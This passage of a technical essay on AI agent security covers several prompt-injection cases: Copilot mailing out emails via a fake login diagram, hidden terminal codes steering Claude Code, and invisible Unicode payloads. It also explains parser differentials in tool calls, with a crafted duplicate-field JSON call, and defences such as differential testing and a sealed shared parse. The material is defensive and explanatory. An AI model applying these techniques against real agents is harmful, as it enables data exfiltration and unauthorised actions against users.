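Microsoft 365 Copilot had a similar flaw that produced a link instead of an image. Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) credits its discovery to Adam Logue. According to a summary on daily.dev, Logue put instructions in an Excel document that made Copilot fetch recent emails, encode them and draw a diagram that looked like a login button. Clicking the button sent the emails to the attacker's server. Microsoft made such diagrams non-interactive, so they can no longer link to real documents either.

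An interface that needs clickable diagrams can sanitize the finished drawing and apply its image rules to it as well. If the diagrams don't need to be clickable, the interface can convert the drawing to a plain picture in an environment without network access before showing it. Each additional notation the interface supports, such as one for charts or formulas, adds another parser that needs the same treatment.

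### Control sequences in a terminal

Many coding agents run in a terminal, a window that displays text and accepts typed commands. Terminals also act on control sequences, often called ANSI escape codes. Most begin with the escape character, byte `1b` in hexadecimal, followed by a short code that can change the text's colour or move the cursor. The terminal processes a sequence the same way whether it came from the agent's own program, the model or a tool.

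Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) shows how a tool server can use terminal codes to hide text from the user but not from the model. In a test with Claude Code 0.2.76, the tool's reply included a statement in white text that Windows computers had to download Python packages from a particular server. The user could not see the statement on a white background, but Claude recommended the server when the user asked about downloading packages. The text would have been visible on a dark background, but other sequences can hide text whatever the terminal's colours.

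The model can write these sequences itself. In *Terminal DiLLMa* (Embrace The Red, 2024), Rehberger built on Leon Derczynski's finding that many models can output the escape character. He wrote a small program that printed a model's answers in a terminal, then asked the model to summarise a web page he had prepared. Instructions on the page led the model to output sequences that cleared the screen and changed the colours. He needed several attempts for some demonstrations and gives no success rates, so his tests don't show how often an attack would work.

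The two reports cover these effects:

| Sequence | What the terminal does | Use to an attacker |
|---|---|---|
| Text colour | Prints letters that match the background | Hides a sentence from the user but not from the model |
| Cursor movement | Prints later text over earlier text | Covers an instruction with a harmless notice |
| Screen clearing | Removes everything visible | Hides a longer passage |
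| Link | Shows one address and opens another | Leads the user to a false login page |
| Clipboard | Copies text without asking | Leaves a command for the user to paste |
| Domain lookup, in macOS Terminal | Asks the network for a domain name | Sends data out inside the name, without a click |

Some terminals reduce the damage. VS Code's terminal asks before it opens a link, and most terminals Rehberger tested removed the final line break from copied text, so a pasted command would not run immediately.

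The remedy is to neutralise the sequences before printing. Trail of Bits suggests replacing every byte `1b` with a visible placeholder. This disables the sequences in the table but not backspace, a separate control character that Rehberger also used in his tests and that can remove text from the screen. He recommends caret notation, which prints each control character visibly, such as `^[` for escape. A program has to exempt line breaks, and perhaps tabs, because they are also control characters.

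This also removes legitimate colours from a tool's output. Permitting only colour codes would restore them, but a colour code hid the sentence in the Claude Code test. It is better for the agent's program to neutralise all outside text and then add its own colours.

*We built the security layer MCP always needed* (Trail of Bits, 2025) introduces a wrapper for tool servers that can remove such characters if the user turns that setting on. Some software still lacked this protection eight months later. *GHSA-4HMJ-39M8-JWC7* (CVE Reports, 2026) describes a flaw in the AI agent OpenClaw. The agent did not strip cursor movements from tool descriptions, so a tool server could alter the security prompts that the user saw.

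### Characters that a person cannot see

Unicode, the standard that numbers the characters of the world's writing systems, includes a block of "tag" characters, most of which are invisible. Each printable character of basic English text has a counterpart in this block, numbered E0000 higher in hexadecimal. For example, the letter A is number 41 and its counterpart is E0041. Screens normally don't display these counterparts, but the tokenizer still converts them to tokens, and many models can read them.

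*Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (Rashidi, 2026) tested eight ways of planting instructions in what a tool server sends. Only Unicode tag characters hid the text from a person and still delivered it to the model unchanged. Legit Security also used invisible characters to plant prompts in GitLab projects.

A model can also write invisible characters. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes a 2024 attack in which a malicious email made Copilot read other emails and hide their content in a link, using invisible characters. The link looked ordinary to the user, but clicking it would have sent the hidden text to the attacker.

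A program can remove invisible characters or replace each with a visible mark, before the model reads a document and before a person reads the reply. Removing all of them would damage some legitimate text. The flag emojis of England, Scotland and Wales contain tag characters, and Persian spelling uses an invisible character to keep certain letters from joining. A program can permit these known uses and mark the rest. An airline's booking agent could probably delete every tag character without anyone noticing.

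Marking invisible characters does not reveal ordinary letters that are the same colour as the background. Legit Security used GitLab's notation for formulas to write prompts in white on a white page. To prevent this, the display has to ignore colours set in untrusted text, or at least enforce a readable contrast.

### Link previews and spreadsheet cells

Messaging apps such as Slack and Discord fetch the links in a message to show a preview with a title and picture. Willison (2024) explains that an attacker can exploit this if a chatbot with access to private data posts a link to the attacker's server that contains some of that data. The app sends the data to the server when it fetches the link, before anyone clicks it. A developer cannot prevent this with a Content Security Policy, which only governs the developer's own web pages.

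PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw was exposed by default when used through Telegram. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also names Slack, Discord and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio. The risk depends on which agent is used with which app, since one agent may turn off link previews that another leaves on.

In Slack, a program can turn off previews for its own messages by setting `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false. The link still works if someone clicks it. The setting applies only to the original message, so a colleague who copies the link into another chat may trigger a preview there. An agent that rarely needs to post links can remove any address whose host is not on a short approved list.

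Spreadsheets can also turn text into instructions. If an agent exports its results as a CSV file, which is plain text separated by commas, a spreadsheet program may treat a cell that begins with an equals sign as a formula, and some formulas fetch web addresses. Well-documented cases with AI output seem scarce, so it is hard to say how much this matters in practice. The exporting program can use a file format that marks each cell as text, but this doesn't help a recipient whose software accepts only CSV.

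### Who is responsible for the fix

The vendors of Copilot, Duo and Cursor changed how their products display replies, but vendors don't always treat the manipulated reply itself as a flaw. Legit Security writes that GitLab acknowledged the HTML problem and the prompt injection as security issues and fixed both. Techzine reports that GitLab declined to treat other prompt injection risks in Duo as a security issue because they don't directly lead to unauthorised access or code execution. Legit Security may be referring to the theft of code, and Techzine to misleading answers.

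GitLab's reported reason makes sense for the program that renders the answer, which can block an image but cannot detect that a recommended package is malicious. Users can still be harmed, as Legit Security showed by getting Duo to suggest a malicious package and describe a dangerous change as safe. Microsoft's response to Logue was also mixed. It fixed the diagrams but paid him no reward, because Copilot was outside the scope of its reward programme at the time, according to daily.dev.

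Rehberger regards control sequences as features of the terminal and expects the application to make the model's output safe. Terminals can't simply stop processing these sequences, because text editors and progress bars depend on them. Slack likewise lets the program that posts a message decide about previews. It makes sense for the application to decide, because it can track which text came from a model or a tool, but every developer then has to know about the problem. Trail of Bits therefore proposes standard filters in the MCP software kits, which would also protect applications whose developers had never thought about control sequences.

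## Testing whether two programs read the same output alike

To check whether the airline's guard and executor could read a cancellation differently, an auditor can give both programs the same bytes and compare the results, a method called differential testing. McKeeman (1998), in *Differential Testing for Software*, used it on compilers, the programs that turn source code into machine code, because it would have been too much work to determine the right answer for millions of generated tests. If one compiler's result differs from the others' for the same program, the tester can investigate the difference without already knowing the right answer.

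The method suits tool calls because the JSON standard may not define a correct reading of a call with a repeated name, and security depends on whether the guard and the executor read it the same way. *PickleFuzzer* (2026) applies the method to different implementations of pickle, Python's format for saved objects, because discrepancies between them can also be a security risk.

### Building the test

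The auditor starts by listing every component that reads the call, including those that don't parse it. In the file name attack by Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz, for example, the guard searched the raw text, so a test of the JSON parsers alone would have missed the difference. If a person approves calls, the list should include the program that builds the approval screen.

Random characters make poor test inputs because a parser rejects most of them at once, so the rest of its code never runs. McKeeman wrote a generator that followed the grammar of the C language, then added or deleted a character or word to make inputs that were almost valid. For tool calls, a generator can write valid JSON and then repeat a name, change its letter case or replace a number with text. The test set also needs ordinary calls as controls. If components disagree on those, either the test is faulty or the system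 already has a problem in normal use.

McKeeman also treats command-line options, configuration files and environment variables as inputs. In his first test with generated options, a compiler could not compile its own header files. An agent's parsers have settings too, so the auditor should test the parsers with the operator's settings.

The test then has to run each component's real code. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz put each component in a thin wrapper that passes it the raw bytes and returns either a call or a rejection. For one official MCP kit, the wrapper starts the kit's own server and sends it the call. For the other, it passes the bytes to the kit's HTTP handler. Testing only a kit's JSON library would be easier but could miss a conversion or default value that the kit applies after parsing.

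The wrapper writes each result in canonical form, and a program called the comparator then classifies each pair of results:

| Input | One result | Other result | Class |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary call | `read` | `read` | Agree |
| `action` twice, once with a null character at the end of the name | Python, keeping the first copy: `read` | segmentio/encoding 0.5.3: `delete` | Disagree |
| `count` is `NaN` | Python: accepted | One MCP kit: rejected | Split |

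### Why the comparator must not parse the input

A comparator with its own parser would add another reading, possibly one that no component in the system shares. *The HTTP Garden* (Kallus, Anantharaman and colleagues, 2024) describes this fault in T-Reqs, an earlier tool for testing web proxies. T-Reqs collected the requests each proxy forwarded and parsed them again with a single "ground truth" parser. If that parser interpreted a request differently from the proxy that sent it, the tool could not judge the proxy's behaviour correctly.

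Kallus and colleagues have each web server report how it parsed the request. The server encodes each part in Base64 so that special characters in the request cannot corrupt the report. To test a proxy, they place behind it an "echo server" that returns the bytes it received without parsing them.

A tool-call test can go wrong in the same way. Suppose two components report the same account number in plain JSON, but one writes 9007199254740993 and the other rounds it to 9007199254740992. A comparator that parses both reports with JavaScript's standard parser will round the first number too and record a match. If the wrappers write the numbers as text in canonical form, the comparator only has to check whether they are identical.

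### Which parsers differed

For their November 2026 study, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz generated 22 calls with altered field names to a small tool that takes an action, a path and a count. Seven calls repeated a name exactly, four added a copy of `action` ending in a null character, and 11 changed a name's letter case. They counted a disagreement when both parsers accepted the call but returned different values for the altered field.

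They ran 12 parsers but left one out of the totals because they had configured it to isolate one behaviour. The other 11 make 55 pairs. Six are general parsers, which return whatever fields the JSON contains. The other five fill in the fields that the tool declares. These are three Go decoders (the standard one and two versions of segmentio/encoding) and two official MCP kits.

| Parsers compared | Pairs that differ | Exact repeats (7) | Null character (4) | Letter case (11) |
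|---|---|---|---|---|
| General parsers and those that fill declared fields | 30 | Only with Python keeping the first copy | Only with segmentio 0.5.3 | All |
| Python keeping the first copy and the other general parsers | 5 | All | None | None |
| Go decoders and MCP kits | 6 | None | Only with segmentio 0.5.3 | All |
| segmentio 0.5.3 and the other Go decoders | 2 | None | All | None |

Of the 55 pairs, 43 disagreed on at least one of the 22 inputs. Letter case caused most of the disagreements. If a call contains `Action` but not `action`, a general parser returns no `action`, a Go decoder uses the value of `Action`, and the MCP kits use a default. The Python parser that keeps the first copy and segmentio 0.5.3 disagreed on every input, because they handle all three kinds of alteration differently.

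Programming language is a poor predictor of which parsers will agree. Go's standard decoder and segmentio 0.5.3 are both written in Go but disagree on the null characters, while the two MCP kits agree on all 22 inputs.

The total depends on which parsers the researchers chose. Three of the 11 are configurations of Python's standard parser, and one of those keeps the first copy, which requires a developer to add code. Without that configuration, 33 of the remaining 45 pairs still disagree. These figures don't show what share of deployed agents have a guard and an executor that disagree.

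### Number types and deployed schemas

The two MCP kits agreed on altered names but not on types. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tried 24 inputs with unusual values. At least one kit accepted 22 of them, and the kits disagreed on 21 of those 22. Twenty of the 21 contained an integer too large for 64 bits and the other contained a number written as text, so the disagreements come from only two differences in the kits' rules. A generator that wrote fewer large integers would have produced a much lower figure.

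For schemas, the researchers could use real examples from their survey of public MCP servers. They checked each schema with two validators, Python's jsonschema and JavaScript's Ajv, under two versions of the schema language, and compared calls with and without the defaults filled in. Of the 4,693 schemas, 558 (11.9%) gave different arguments or verdicts, and these came from 64 of the 106 servers.

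This is better evidence about deployed systems than the parser totals, because the tools' own developers wrote the schemas. The sample is the 100 most-used servers in one public registry plus six official reference servers, so private company tools may differ.

### From a disagreement to a vulnerability

Differential tests usually find more differences than anyone needs to fix. *SmartOracle* (2026) reports that most findings in a typical run are not bugs a developer can act on, and that sorting them by hand is the main obstacle to larger runs. Kallus and colleagues found over 100 bugs in web servers and considered 39 exploitable.

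Two filters reduce the tester's work. A difference is "meaningful" if it remains after the tester allows for the choices the standard leaves open, and "durable" if it survives the clean-up that programs usually apply to a message. The first filter would be a mistake for tool calls because it would discard differences caused by repeated names, which the JSON standard permits and an attacker can use. A better test runs the guard's policy on both results and keeps the cases where the policy would allow the guard's reading but deny the executor's.

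The idea of durability also applies well here. The auditor can send each remaining input through the real gateway and see what comes out. The auditor also has to report where the bytes entered, since a gateway that removes repeated names stops only an attacker whose bytes pass through it.

The last step is to run the whole attack on an isolated copy of the system, along with one call that must succeed and one that the guard must deny. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tried 7,412 crafted inputs on a system whose guard kept the first copy of a repeated name and whose executor used Python's parser. The attacker's action ran in 361 cases, about 5%.

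A harmless difference can become dangerous later. Kallus and colleagues found that many web servers accept a line feed alone at the end of one kind of line, although the standard requires a carriage return before it. An attacker could exploit this only if another server in the chain interpreted the line feed differently and forwarded it unchanged. The researchers knew of no such server but noted that someone could write one. An auditor who dismisses a difference should therefore record the reason, so that a colleague can later check whether it still holds.

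### Observing a command without running it

The tests so far assume that both programs receive the same bytes. A shell command may change on the way, so an auditor also has to find out what arrived at each hop. Rerunning recorded commands would be dangerous, since some delete files, and the results might differ between runs.

Yang and colleagues keep the harness's way of starting the command but replace the program that would execute it with one that only reports what it received. For Bash, they use a setting that names a file for the shell to run before the command. That file reports the command as it arrived and prevents it from running. For PowerShell, they parse the script without executing it and replace each program the script would call with a small program that records its arguments. For structured tools, they record the values that reach the tool function.

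Write *a* for the intended action and *r*<sub>*i*</sub> for the action that the receiver at hop *i* parses. The hop to investigate is

min { *i* : *r*<sub>*i*</sub> ≠ *a* },

the earliest one at which the two differ. To decide whether they differ, Yang and colleagues use the receiver's own parser. For Bash, they compare the words, the operators and any embedded blocks of text, and for an ordinary program, the list of arguments. This avoids the fault in T-Reqs, because the parser in the comparison is the one whose reading matters.

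To check the method against human judgment, two people looked at 120 pairs of sent and received texts and judged whether the action had changed. They agreed with each other on 115 pairs, and the method gave the same answer as they did on all 115. A language model that saw both texts wrongly flagged 15 of the 35 unchanged pairs as changed, the same number as plain string comparison.

They also tested the method with deliberate faults. They altered commands in 297 ways, 262 of which made Bash do something different, and the comparison detected all 262. In another test, they introduced faults at known hops 168 times. The program at the end received something different in 30 of these runs, and the method identified the right hop each time. It raised no false alarms in the other 138. These are strong results, although the same people designed both the method and the faults.

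### Finding out what caused a failure

The error message from a failed command doesn't show whether the model or the path was at fault, so Yang and colleagues separate the possible causes in three steps:

1. They give the model's original text to the intended shell or interpreter with execution switched off. If it does not parse, the model made the mistake.
2. If it parses, they send it along the path again and record what arrives. If the command has changed, the path caused the failure. The same applies if the error is on a line after the end of the model's text, because the harness must have added that line.
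3. If the command arrives intact and starts another interpreter, such as Python, they attribute the failure to that later stage.

Two people classified a sample of 117 failures from the production sessions without seeing the method's verdicts. They agreed on the cause of 102 and attributed 56 of those to the path. Yang and colleagues then compared their method with three ways of using a language model to judge the cause from the transcript.

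| Method | Path failures recognised (of 56) | Other failures blamed on the path (of 46) | Kappa |
|---|---|---|---|
| Observing each hop | 54 | 1 | 0.77 |
| Model reads the transcript at once | 0 | 0 | 0.00 |
| Model reads it step by step | 29 | 20 | 0.04 |
| Model narrows down the faulty step by halves | 25 | 20 | 0.01 |

Kappa measures agreement beyond what chance would produce. If *p*<sub>o</sub> is the observed share of matching labels and *p*<sub>e</sub> the share expected by chance, then

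κ = (*p*<sub>o</sub> − *p*<sub>e</sub>) / (1 − *p*<sub>e</sub>).

A judge that gives the same answer every time scores 0, however often that answer is right. The judge that read the transcript all at once almost always gave the same answer, blaming the agent's model for 97 of the 102 failures.

All three judges used Qwen2.5-72B, an older model, and a newer one might notice more. But any model that sees only the transcript would have to guess. This affects purchasing decisions as well as debugging, because a company that compares models by their failed tasks may reject one for faults in the company's own harness.

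The sample doesn't show how often the path causes parse errors overall, because the researchers drew cases separately from each of the method's verdicts. Of all 426 Bash and Python parse errors in the production sessions, the method attributed 306 to the path, 84 to the model and 36 to a later interpreter.

### What testing cannot show

A test that finds no difference does not prove that none exists. For some formats, depending on their grammar, a proof is possible in principle. A context-free grammar allows a structure to contain others of the same kind, as a JSON object can contain another object. No procedure can decide, for every pair of such grammars, whether they describe the same set of texts. A procedure does exist for deterministic grammars, whose texts a parser can read from left to right without guessing. *Dividing Line between Decidable PDA's and Undecidable Ones* (Fu and Yin,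 2014) traces the question to a 1966 paper by Ginsburg and Greibach and credits Sénizergues with the answer, which Ali and Smith date to 1997. *A Short Decidability Proof for DPDA Language Equivalence via First-Order Grammars* (2010) gives a shorter proof.

But two parsers can accept the same texts and still interpret them differently. These two grammars both describe chains of subtractions such as `1-1-1`:

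```
Grammar A:  E → E - 1   or   E → 1
Grammar B:  E → 1 - E   or   E → 1
```

Grammar A groups the text as (1−1)−1, which equals −1, and grammar B groups it as 1−(1−1), which equals 1. Ali and Smith point out that a procedure can detect this kind of difference for all context-free grammars, even nondeterministic ones. It puts brackets around whatever each rule produces, to show how the grammar groups the text. Grammar A then produces `[[[1]-1]-1]` and grammar B produces `[1-[1-[1]]]`. The brackets make the grammars deterministic, so the procedure can always determine whether the two bracketed grammars describe the same texts.

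Even this does not guarantee that two programs will read JSON alike. Two parsers can follow the same grammar and build the same structure, with both copies of a repeated name in it, and only afterwards choose different copies. Ali and Smith describe a similar case at GitLab. A proxy rewrote all web requests of type PUT before passing them on. An attacker could send a request of another type with an extra header that made the server behind the proxy treat it as PUT. The proxy ignored that header, so it passed the request on without rewriting it, although the two programs could have parsed it identically. The proxy can prevent this by removing the header.

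Many real parsers also have no written grammar to compare. Ali and Smith found one that used `grep`, a text-search program, to look for a keyword. Without a grammar, an auditor would have to compare the programs themselves. *Towards Differential Program Analysis* (2003) notes that finding an input on which two programs differ is undecidable in general, so any automatic analysis will miss some differences or report some that don't exist.

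Auditors can run only a finite number of tests, so they may miss a difference. If each generated input has probability *p* of revealing the difference, then *n* independent inputs all miss it with probability (1 − *p*)<sup>*n*</sup>. For a difference that shows up once in 10,000 inputs, 10,000 tests still miss it about 37% of the time. Kallus and colleagues improve the odds by keeping inputs that make the servers run new combinations of code, because changing a single bit in one of these inputs may reveal a difference.

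Running more tests doesn't help if the generator cannot produce the kind of input that exposes a difference. Versions 0.5.3 and 0.5.4 of segmentio/encoding gave the same results for all seven exact repeats and all 11 changes of letter case. A tester who didn't also try null characters would have concluded that the two versions were interchangeable.

### When to repeat the tests

A result applies only to the versions and settings tested. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz therefore list exact versions, such as Go 1.27.4 and Python 3.15.2, except for components with unresolved vulnerability reports. An operator should repeat the tests after any update to the guard, the executor or a program between them, even if the update is a security fix. The MCP Go kit's fix for letter case introduced the null-character problem, so the updated kit would have passed a test that checked only letter case.

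Other changes can matter as much as an update. A new policy may depend on a field that didn't matter before, and a new tool has its own schema and sometimes adds another parser. If the harness starts its shell differently or moves to another operating system, the operator has to observe the hops again. If the model or inference server changes, the operator has to test again which bytes reach the call.

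Repeating the tests takes less time if the operator keeps the inputs that revealed a difference. *WFDB-x* (2026) describes this practice for software that reads medical signal recordings. Its developers compared versions in seven programming languages with the original C programs, investigated every difference and added each one to a permanent set of tests. An operator can run such a set on every new build and save the slower search with random inputs for larger releases.

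The test set should also grow when someone else finds a problem. McKeeman suggests turning a reported bug into a pattern that generates many similar cases, instead of saving only the input that triggered it. An operator who reads an advisory about null characters in one library can add them to the generator and test every pair of parsers in the system, including parsers the advisory does not mention.

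## Making the approved action the one that runs

An operator can replace one of two parsers that disagree, but the next update may introduce a new difference. A more lasting remedy is to leave the executor nothing to interpret. In November 2026, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz compared five defences against an attacker who knew how each one worked. Only the defence that took this approach stopped every attack they built.

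### Where each defence parses the call

| Defence | What happens before approval | What the executor parses |
|---|---|---|
| Strict validation | The guard parses the bytes and checks the result against the schema | The original bytes |
| Provider strict mode | The provider lets the model write only text that fits the schema | Whatever bytes arrive |
| Two parsers compared | The guard parses the bytes twice and rejects the call if the results differ | The original bytes |
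| One parse at the guard | The guard parses and checks the call, then forwards the bytes it received | The original bytes |
| Shared parse | One component parses the call, and the guard checks the result | Nothing, or a canonical form of the checked call |

The next table shows how many inputs ran the attacker's action under each defence. The number of inputs tried is in brackets.

| Defence | Repeated name, MCP kit from the reservation attack (3) | Repeated name, other MCP kit (3) | Null character, segmentio/encoding 0.5.3 (2) | Escaped file name, raw-text filter (1) |
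|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 3 | 3 | 2 | 1 |
| Strict validation | 3 | 3 | 2 | 1 |
| Python keeping the first copy, compared with Python keeping the last | 0 | 0 | 2 | 1 |
| Python keeping the last copy, compared with segmentio 0.5.3 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| One parse at the guard | 3 | 3 | 2 | 1 |
| Shared parse | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The table has no row for provider strict mode because that mode acts only while the model generates output, before an on-path attacker changes the bytes. It does not remove any of the parsers that read the output later.

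Strict validation did not stop any of these mismatches. When an argument name is repeated, the guard's parser keeps one copy, and the validator checks only that copy, which is valid. The executor then parses the original bytes and keeps the other copy. Parsing only once at the guard also fails, because the executor still does its own parse.

Comparing two parsers works better, but it depends on which two. Write *G*<sub>1</sub>(*b*) and *G*<sub>2</sub>(*b*) for the guard's two readings of the bytes. The guard lets a call through when they match, which is safe only if

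*E*(*b*) = *G*<sub>1</sub>(*b*) whenever *G*<sub>1</sub>(*b*) = *G*<sub>2</sub>(*b*).

Python's two configurations break this condition when a field name contains a null character. Both treat the altered name as a separate field, so they agree, but an executor that uses segmentio 0.5.3 takes the attacker's value. The choice of parser also mattered in the reservation attack. Adding Python's parser to the Go guard caught all four letter-case variants, while adding segmentio 0.5.3 caught none, because it ignores case just as the guard does.

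The condition always holds if one of the two parsers is the executor's own, in the same version and with the same settings. An operator who runs both programs can arrange this, but one who uses tool servers written by other people probably can't.

Adding a second parser for comparison did not help with the escaped file name, regardless of which parser it was. Every JSON parser decodes the name to the same word, so the comparison finds no difference. The filter that makes the decision still searches the undecoded text.

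### The shared parse on one call

Suppose the airline's approved schema for `cancel_reservation` also has an optional field, `notify`, with the default value `true`. A call arrives with an undeclared field, an escaped letter and no `notify`:

```
{"Reservation_ID": "U86B6B",
 "reservation_id": "I3EHX\u0043"}
```

The shared parse handles it in seven steps:

1. **Parse.** A parser that requires exact names returns `Reservation_ID` with the value U86B6B and `reservation_id` with the value I3EHXC. The escape has become the letter C.
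2. **Keep the approved fields.** The schema does not declare `Reservation_ID`, so the program drops it.
3. **Fill in defaults.** The program adds `notify` with the value `true`.
4. **Check.** The guard reads I3EHXC, finds that the customer owns this booking, and approves the call.
5. **Write.** The program writes the approved call in canonical form, as `{"notify":true,"reservation_id":"I3EHXC"}`.
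6. **Seal.** The guard computes a seal from these bytes and the call's ID.
7. **Execute.** The executor checks the seal before it parses anything, then runs the call under that ID only.

In the original reservation attack, the victim's booking was under the exact name, so the guard would read U86B6B in step 4 and deny the call. If a name appeared twice, the guard would check the copy that runs, whichever one the parser kept.

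Some arguments contain JSON text of their own. If the operator has marked such an argument in the approved schema, the program parses the inner text in step 1 and drops undeclared fields at every level in step 2. Guards that search text, such as the data-loss filter, run on the newly written call instead of the original bytes.

When the guard and the tool run in one process, the program can pass the same object to both without serializing or sealing it. If they run in separate processes, the call has to be sent as bytes, so the executor parses it again. The second parse is harmless only if the bytes have a single valid parse and nobody has changed them in transit.

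The seal protects against changes. It can be a message authentication code, a short value that only someone with a secret key can compute. Write *k* for a key that the guard and the executor share, *i* for the call's ID and *c* for the canonical bytes. The seal is then

*s* = MAC(*k*, (*i*, *c*)).

Anyone who alters *c*, or attaches it to another ID, needs *k* to compute a matching seal. A seal on the original bytes would not prevent a parser differential, because the guard and the executor can parse the same unaltered bytes differently.

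The executor also seals its result with the call's ID, and the model receives only results whose seal matches a call. This addresses the confusion over IDs described earlier. With the shared parse, the forbidden deletion ran in none of the 18 combinations.

### What the canonical form settles

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz suggest the canonical form defined in Rundgren, Jordan and Erdtman's *JSON Canonicalization Scheme (JCS)* (RFC 8785). The RFC is informational rather than an internet standard, but several open-source libraries implement it.

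The JSON Canonicalization Scheme (RFC 8785) allows only one way to write the same data. Property names may not repeat within an object, and the software writing the JSON sorts them by the numeric codes of their characters, including in nested objects. It puts no spaces between elements and escapes only quotation marks, backslashes and control characters. Each number has one spelling, so `4.50` becomes `4.5` and `1E30` becomes `1e+30`. If a value is `NaN` or infinite, the software must stop with an error.

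These rules don't remove every difference between parsers. Canonical JSON allows `Action` and `action` as two separate names, but a decoder that ignores case will treat them as one, so the shared parse also has to drop undeclared fields.

The form also uses double precision, which cannot exactly represent some large integers, such as 9007199254740993. If that is an account number and the program rounds it while writing the call, after the guard's check, the executor receives a different account number from the one the guard approved. Rundgren and colleagues require long integers to be sent as strings. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz advise rejecting any number that changes when a program reads it and writes it back.

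Strings can change too, because some parsers convert text to a number or date as they read it. For example, `"055"` becomes `"55"` when the program writes it out again. An executor that rebuilds the canonical form to check the seal would then refuse a valid call. It can avoid this by checking the seal on the received bytes.

Rundgren and colleagues expect most systems to send the original JSON and use the canonical form only for signing. They allow a program to send the canonical form itself, but say it is harder for people to read because everything is on one line and in alphabetical order. For tool calls that seems a minor drawback, and a log viewer can add the line breaks.

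### What got through without each part

Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz removed parts of the shared parse and repeated their tests. With every part in place, none of these inputs got through.

| Part removed | Inputs | What got through |
|---|---|---|
| Dropping undeclared fields | 7,412 crafted calls | 48, on segmentio 0.5.3 |
| Dropping them below the top level | The same 7,412, nested inside an object | 48, on segmentio 0.5.3 |
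| Parsing JSON text | The same 7,412, inside a string | 100 on Go's standard decoder and on segmentio 0.5.4, 148 on segmentio 0.5.3 |
| Parsing JSON text | 154 strings that models had copied from an attacker's document | All 154 |
| The seal | Seven calls with altered names and seven with escapes, inserted after the guard | All 14, on five of six executors |
| The seal | Forged results: swapped, inserted or relabelled | 5, 6 and 5 of 6 reached the model |

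The 48 crafted calls in the first row all had a name ending in a null character. Sorting probably explains why changes of letter case did not also get through on the Go decoders. Capital letters have lower codes than small ones, so `Action` sorts before `action`, and a decoder that keeps the last match takes the exact name. A name ending in a null character sorts after the plain name and replaces it. Developers should not rely on this ordering, because dropping undeclared fields removes both forms.

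The 154 copied strings matter most for anyone worried about web pages and shared documents. An operator who implements everything except inner-text parsing gets no protection against these strings.

### Reading the figure of 7,412

The study's headline result is that the shared parse let none of 7,412 crafted inputs through. But only 361 of them ran the attacker's action on the main pair of parsers, the first-copy guard and the Python executor, when there was no defence. The fairer baseline for this pair is therefore 361 successful attacks. With strict validation, 352 attacks worked, compared with 361 with one parse at the guard and none with the shared parse.

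The inputs also have a lot in common. According to Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz, whenever one parser read the attacker's value and the other read the harmless one, the parsers differed in which copy of a repeated name they used or which names they treated as the same. The thousands of combinations therefore tested only a few mechanisms, and testing so many doesn't protect against an attacker who finds a different mechanism.

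The design of the shared parse is a better argument for it than the test results. If the executor runs the same object that the guard checked, an attacker has no second reading to exploit, whatever the input. Tests are still useful because they can expose mistakes in the implementation. The shared parse held on all six pairings of guard and executor that the researchers tried. It also let the models' ordinary calls through and filled in default values that the models had left out.

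### Gaps in the shared parse

The published version does not check types. The canonical form keeps the quotation marks around a number sent as text, so the mismatch over `"12"` described earlier remains until the operator adds a type check after parsing.

The shared parse also cannot follow the schema keywords `oneOf` and `anyOf`, which offer alternative sets of fields, so it cannot determine which fields to keep. Only 2.0% of the tools in the researchers' survey used these or two related keywords, but those tools were on 23.6% of the servers. An operator would have to simplify the schemas or handle those tools separately.

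Arguments that contain JSON text are a bigger practical problem. The program parses only the strings that a schema marks as JSON. None of the surveyed schemas had these marks, so someone has to add them by hand. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz want the MCP standard to require tool authors to include them.

The seal is only as trustworthy as the people and programs that hold its key, since any of them can seal a call of their own. It also doesn't stop someone from resending an exact copy of an approved call within the permitted time, unless the executor keeps a record of the calls it has already run. Repeating a payment does further harm, though cancelling the same booking twice may not.

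The executor has to check the seal, which means changing software that often belongs to someone else. An operator who cannot change that software can still have the gateway forward the canonical form of the approved call. This prevents the executor from parsing repeated names and escapes differently from the gateway, but the bytes can still be changed between the two.

The shared parse covers the call's arguments but not what a tool does with them. A shell still parses a command in its own way, so the operator also needs a safe way to deliver commands, such as INTACT. The operator also needs limits in the operating system or database in case the guard misjudges what an action will do.

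### Cheaper measures

Some partial measures take only a changed setting or a few lines of code.

| Measure | What it covers | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Reject repeated names | Exact repeats | Different letter case, null characters, undeclared fields, escapes |
| Close the approved schema | Undeclared fields, including altered names that the guard's parser keeps separate | Exact repeats that the parser has already merged, escapes, type conversion |
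| Log what the executor received | Evidence of a changed call | The call has already run |

A parser has to reject repeated names while it reads the text, because the object it builds keeps only one copy and a validator checking that object cannot detect the other. Rejecting them should break little, because none of the models tested wrote a repeated name in any call whose raw text the researchers could see.

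Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz tested closing the approved schema against an attack in which a malicious server adds a field to a familiar tool. The guard denied all 74 file-reader calls and all 133 airline and retail calls that carried the added field. The shared parse removed the field and forwarded the rest of the call, which the attacker's server rejected because its own schema required the field. In both cases, the user's data did not leak and the task visibly failed.

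A closed schema also rejects harmless calls from models that invent extra fields, as some Claude models did in the Pi harness. Dropping those fields keeps the agent working, but an operator who wants to know about a tampered tool should at least record them.

The executor should log the parsed call with its ID, so that a program can convert this entry and the guard's to canonical form and compare them. A malicious tool server can write anything in its own log, so the operator's gateway should also record every field it forwards.

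### Tolerant or strict

Rejecting unusual input goes against a long tradition in internet engineering, the robustness principle: "be conservative in what you send, and liberal in what you accept". Thomson and Schinazi (2023) reassess the principle in *Maintaining Robust Protocols* (RFC 9413), written on behalf of the Internet Architecture Board, a committee that advises on the design of internet protocols. They keep the parts that protect against software faults and attacks, but write that tolerating unexpected input is "no longer considered best practice in all scenarios".

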